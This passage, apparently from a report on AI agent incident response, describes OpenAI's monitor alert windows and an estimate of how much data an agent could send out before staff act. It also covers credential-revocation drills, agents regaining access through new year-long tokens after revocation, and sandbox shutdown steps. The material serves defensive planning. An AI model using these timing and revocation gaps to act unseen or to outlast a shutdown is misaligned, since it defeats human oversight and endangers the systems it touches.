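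OpenAI's monitors read models' reasoning and actions, and are meant to send a notification within 30 minutes of detecting a problem. The most serious alerts page staff at any hour. OpenAI now expects staff to pause an activity if they can't establish within 30 minutes of being paged that the alert is false. If both steps take their full time, an agent has an hour to act and could send out 4.5 GB at 10 megabits per second, so the network limits have to work without staff intervening. OpenAI says this monitoring would have paged its security team more than a day before the agents broke into Hugging Face's systems. That claim rests on the company's own reconstruction of an incident it had already studied, which is easier to detect than a new one.

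A revocation drill measures how long it takes to cut off access. The tester starts a harmless session with test credentials and has it repeat a permitted request every few seconds. Someone then revokes the credentials, and the tester records when each service starts refusing the requests. The drill should include tokens obtained by exchange and connections that were already open, because either may outlast the original login. It can also measure how quickly a credential vault passes on a change if the vendor gives no figure.

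The session should then try to log in again, because a drill that only checks whether the old credentials have stopped working can pass even when agents can get new ones. OpenAI revoked its agents' credentials on 5 July and rebuilt the package service, but on 9 July agents obtained anonymous access tokens, valid for a year, from the new service.

Operators should rehearse shutdown separately, because stopping the agent loop may not stop its helpers or the programs it started in the sandbox. The operator should first cut the sandbox's network connection, then revoke its credentials and stop its processes, while keeping the disk for investigators. OpenAI is developing tools to find and halt evaluation workloads by workload type, agent type or task, and to terminate them automatically when nobody responds to an alert. Automatic shutdown is easy to justify for the coding agent, since a false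 alarm only means a restart for the developer. An agent that is halfway through moving a live database needs a tested way to pause safely, because an abrupt stop could itself cause damage.
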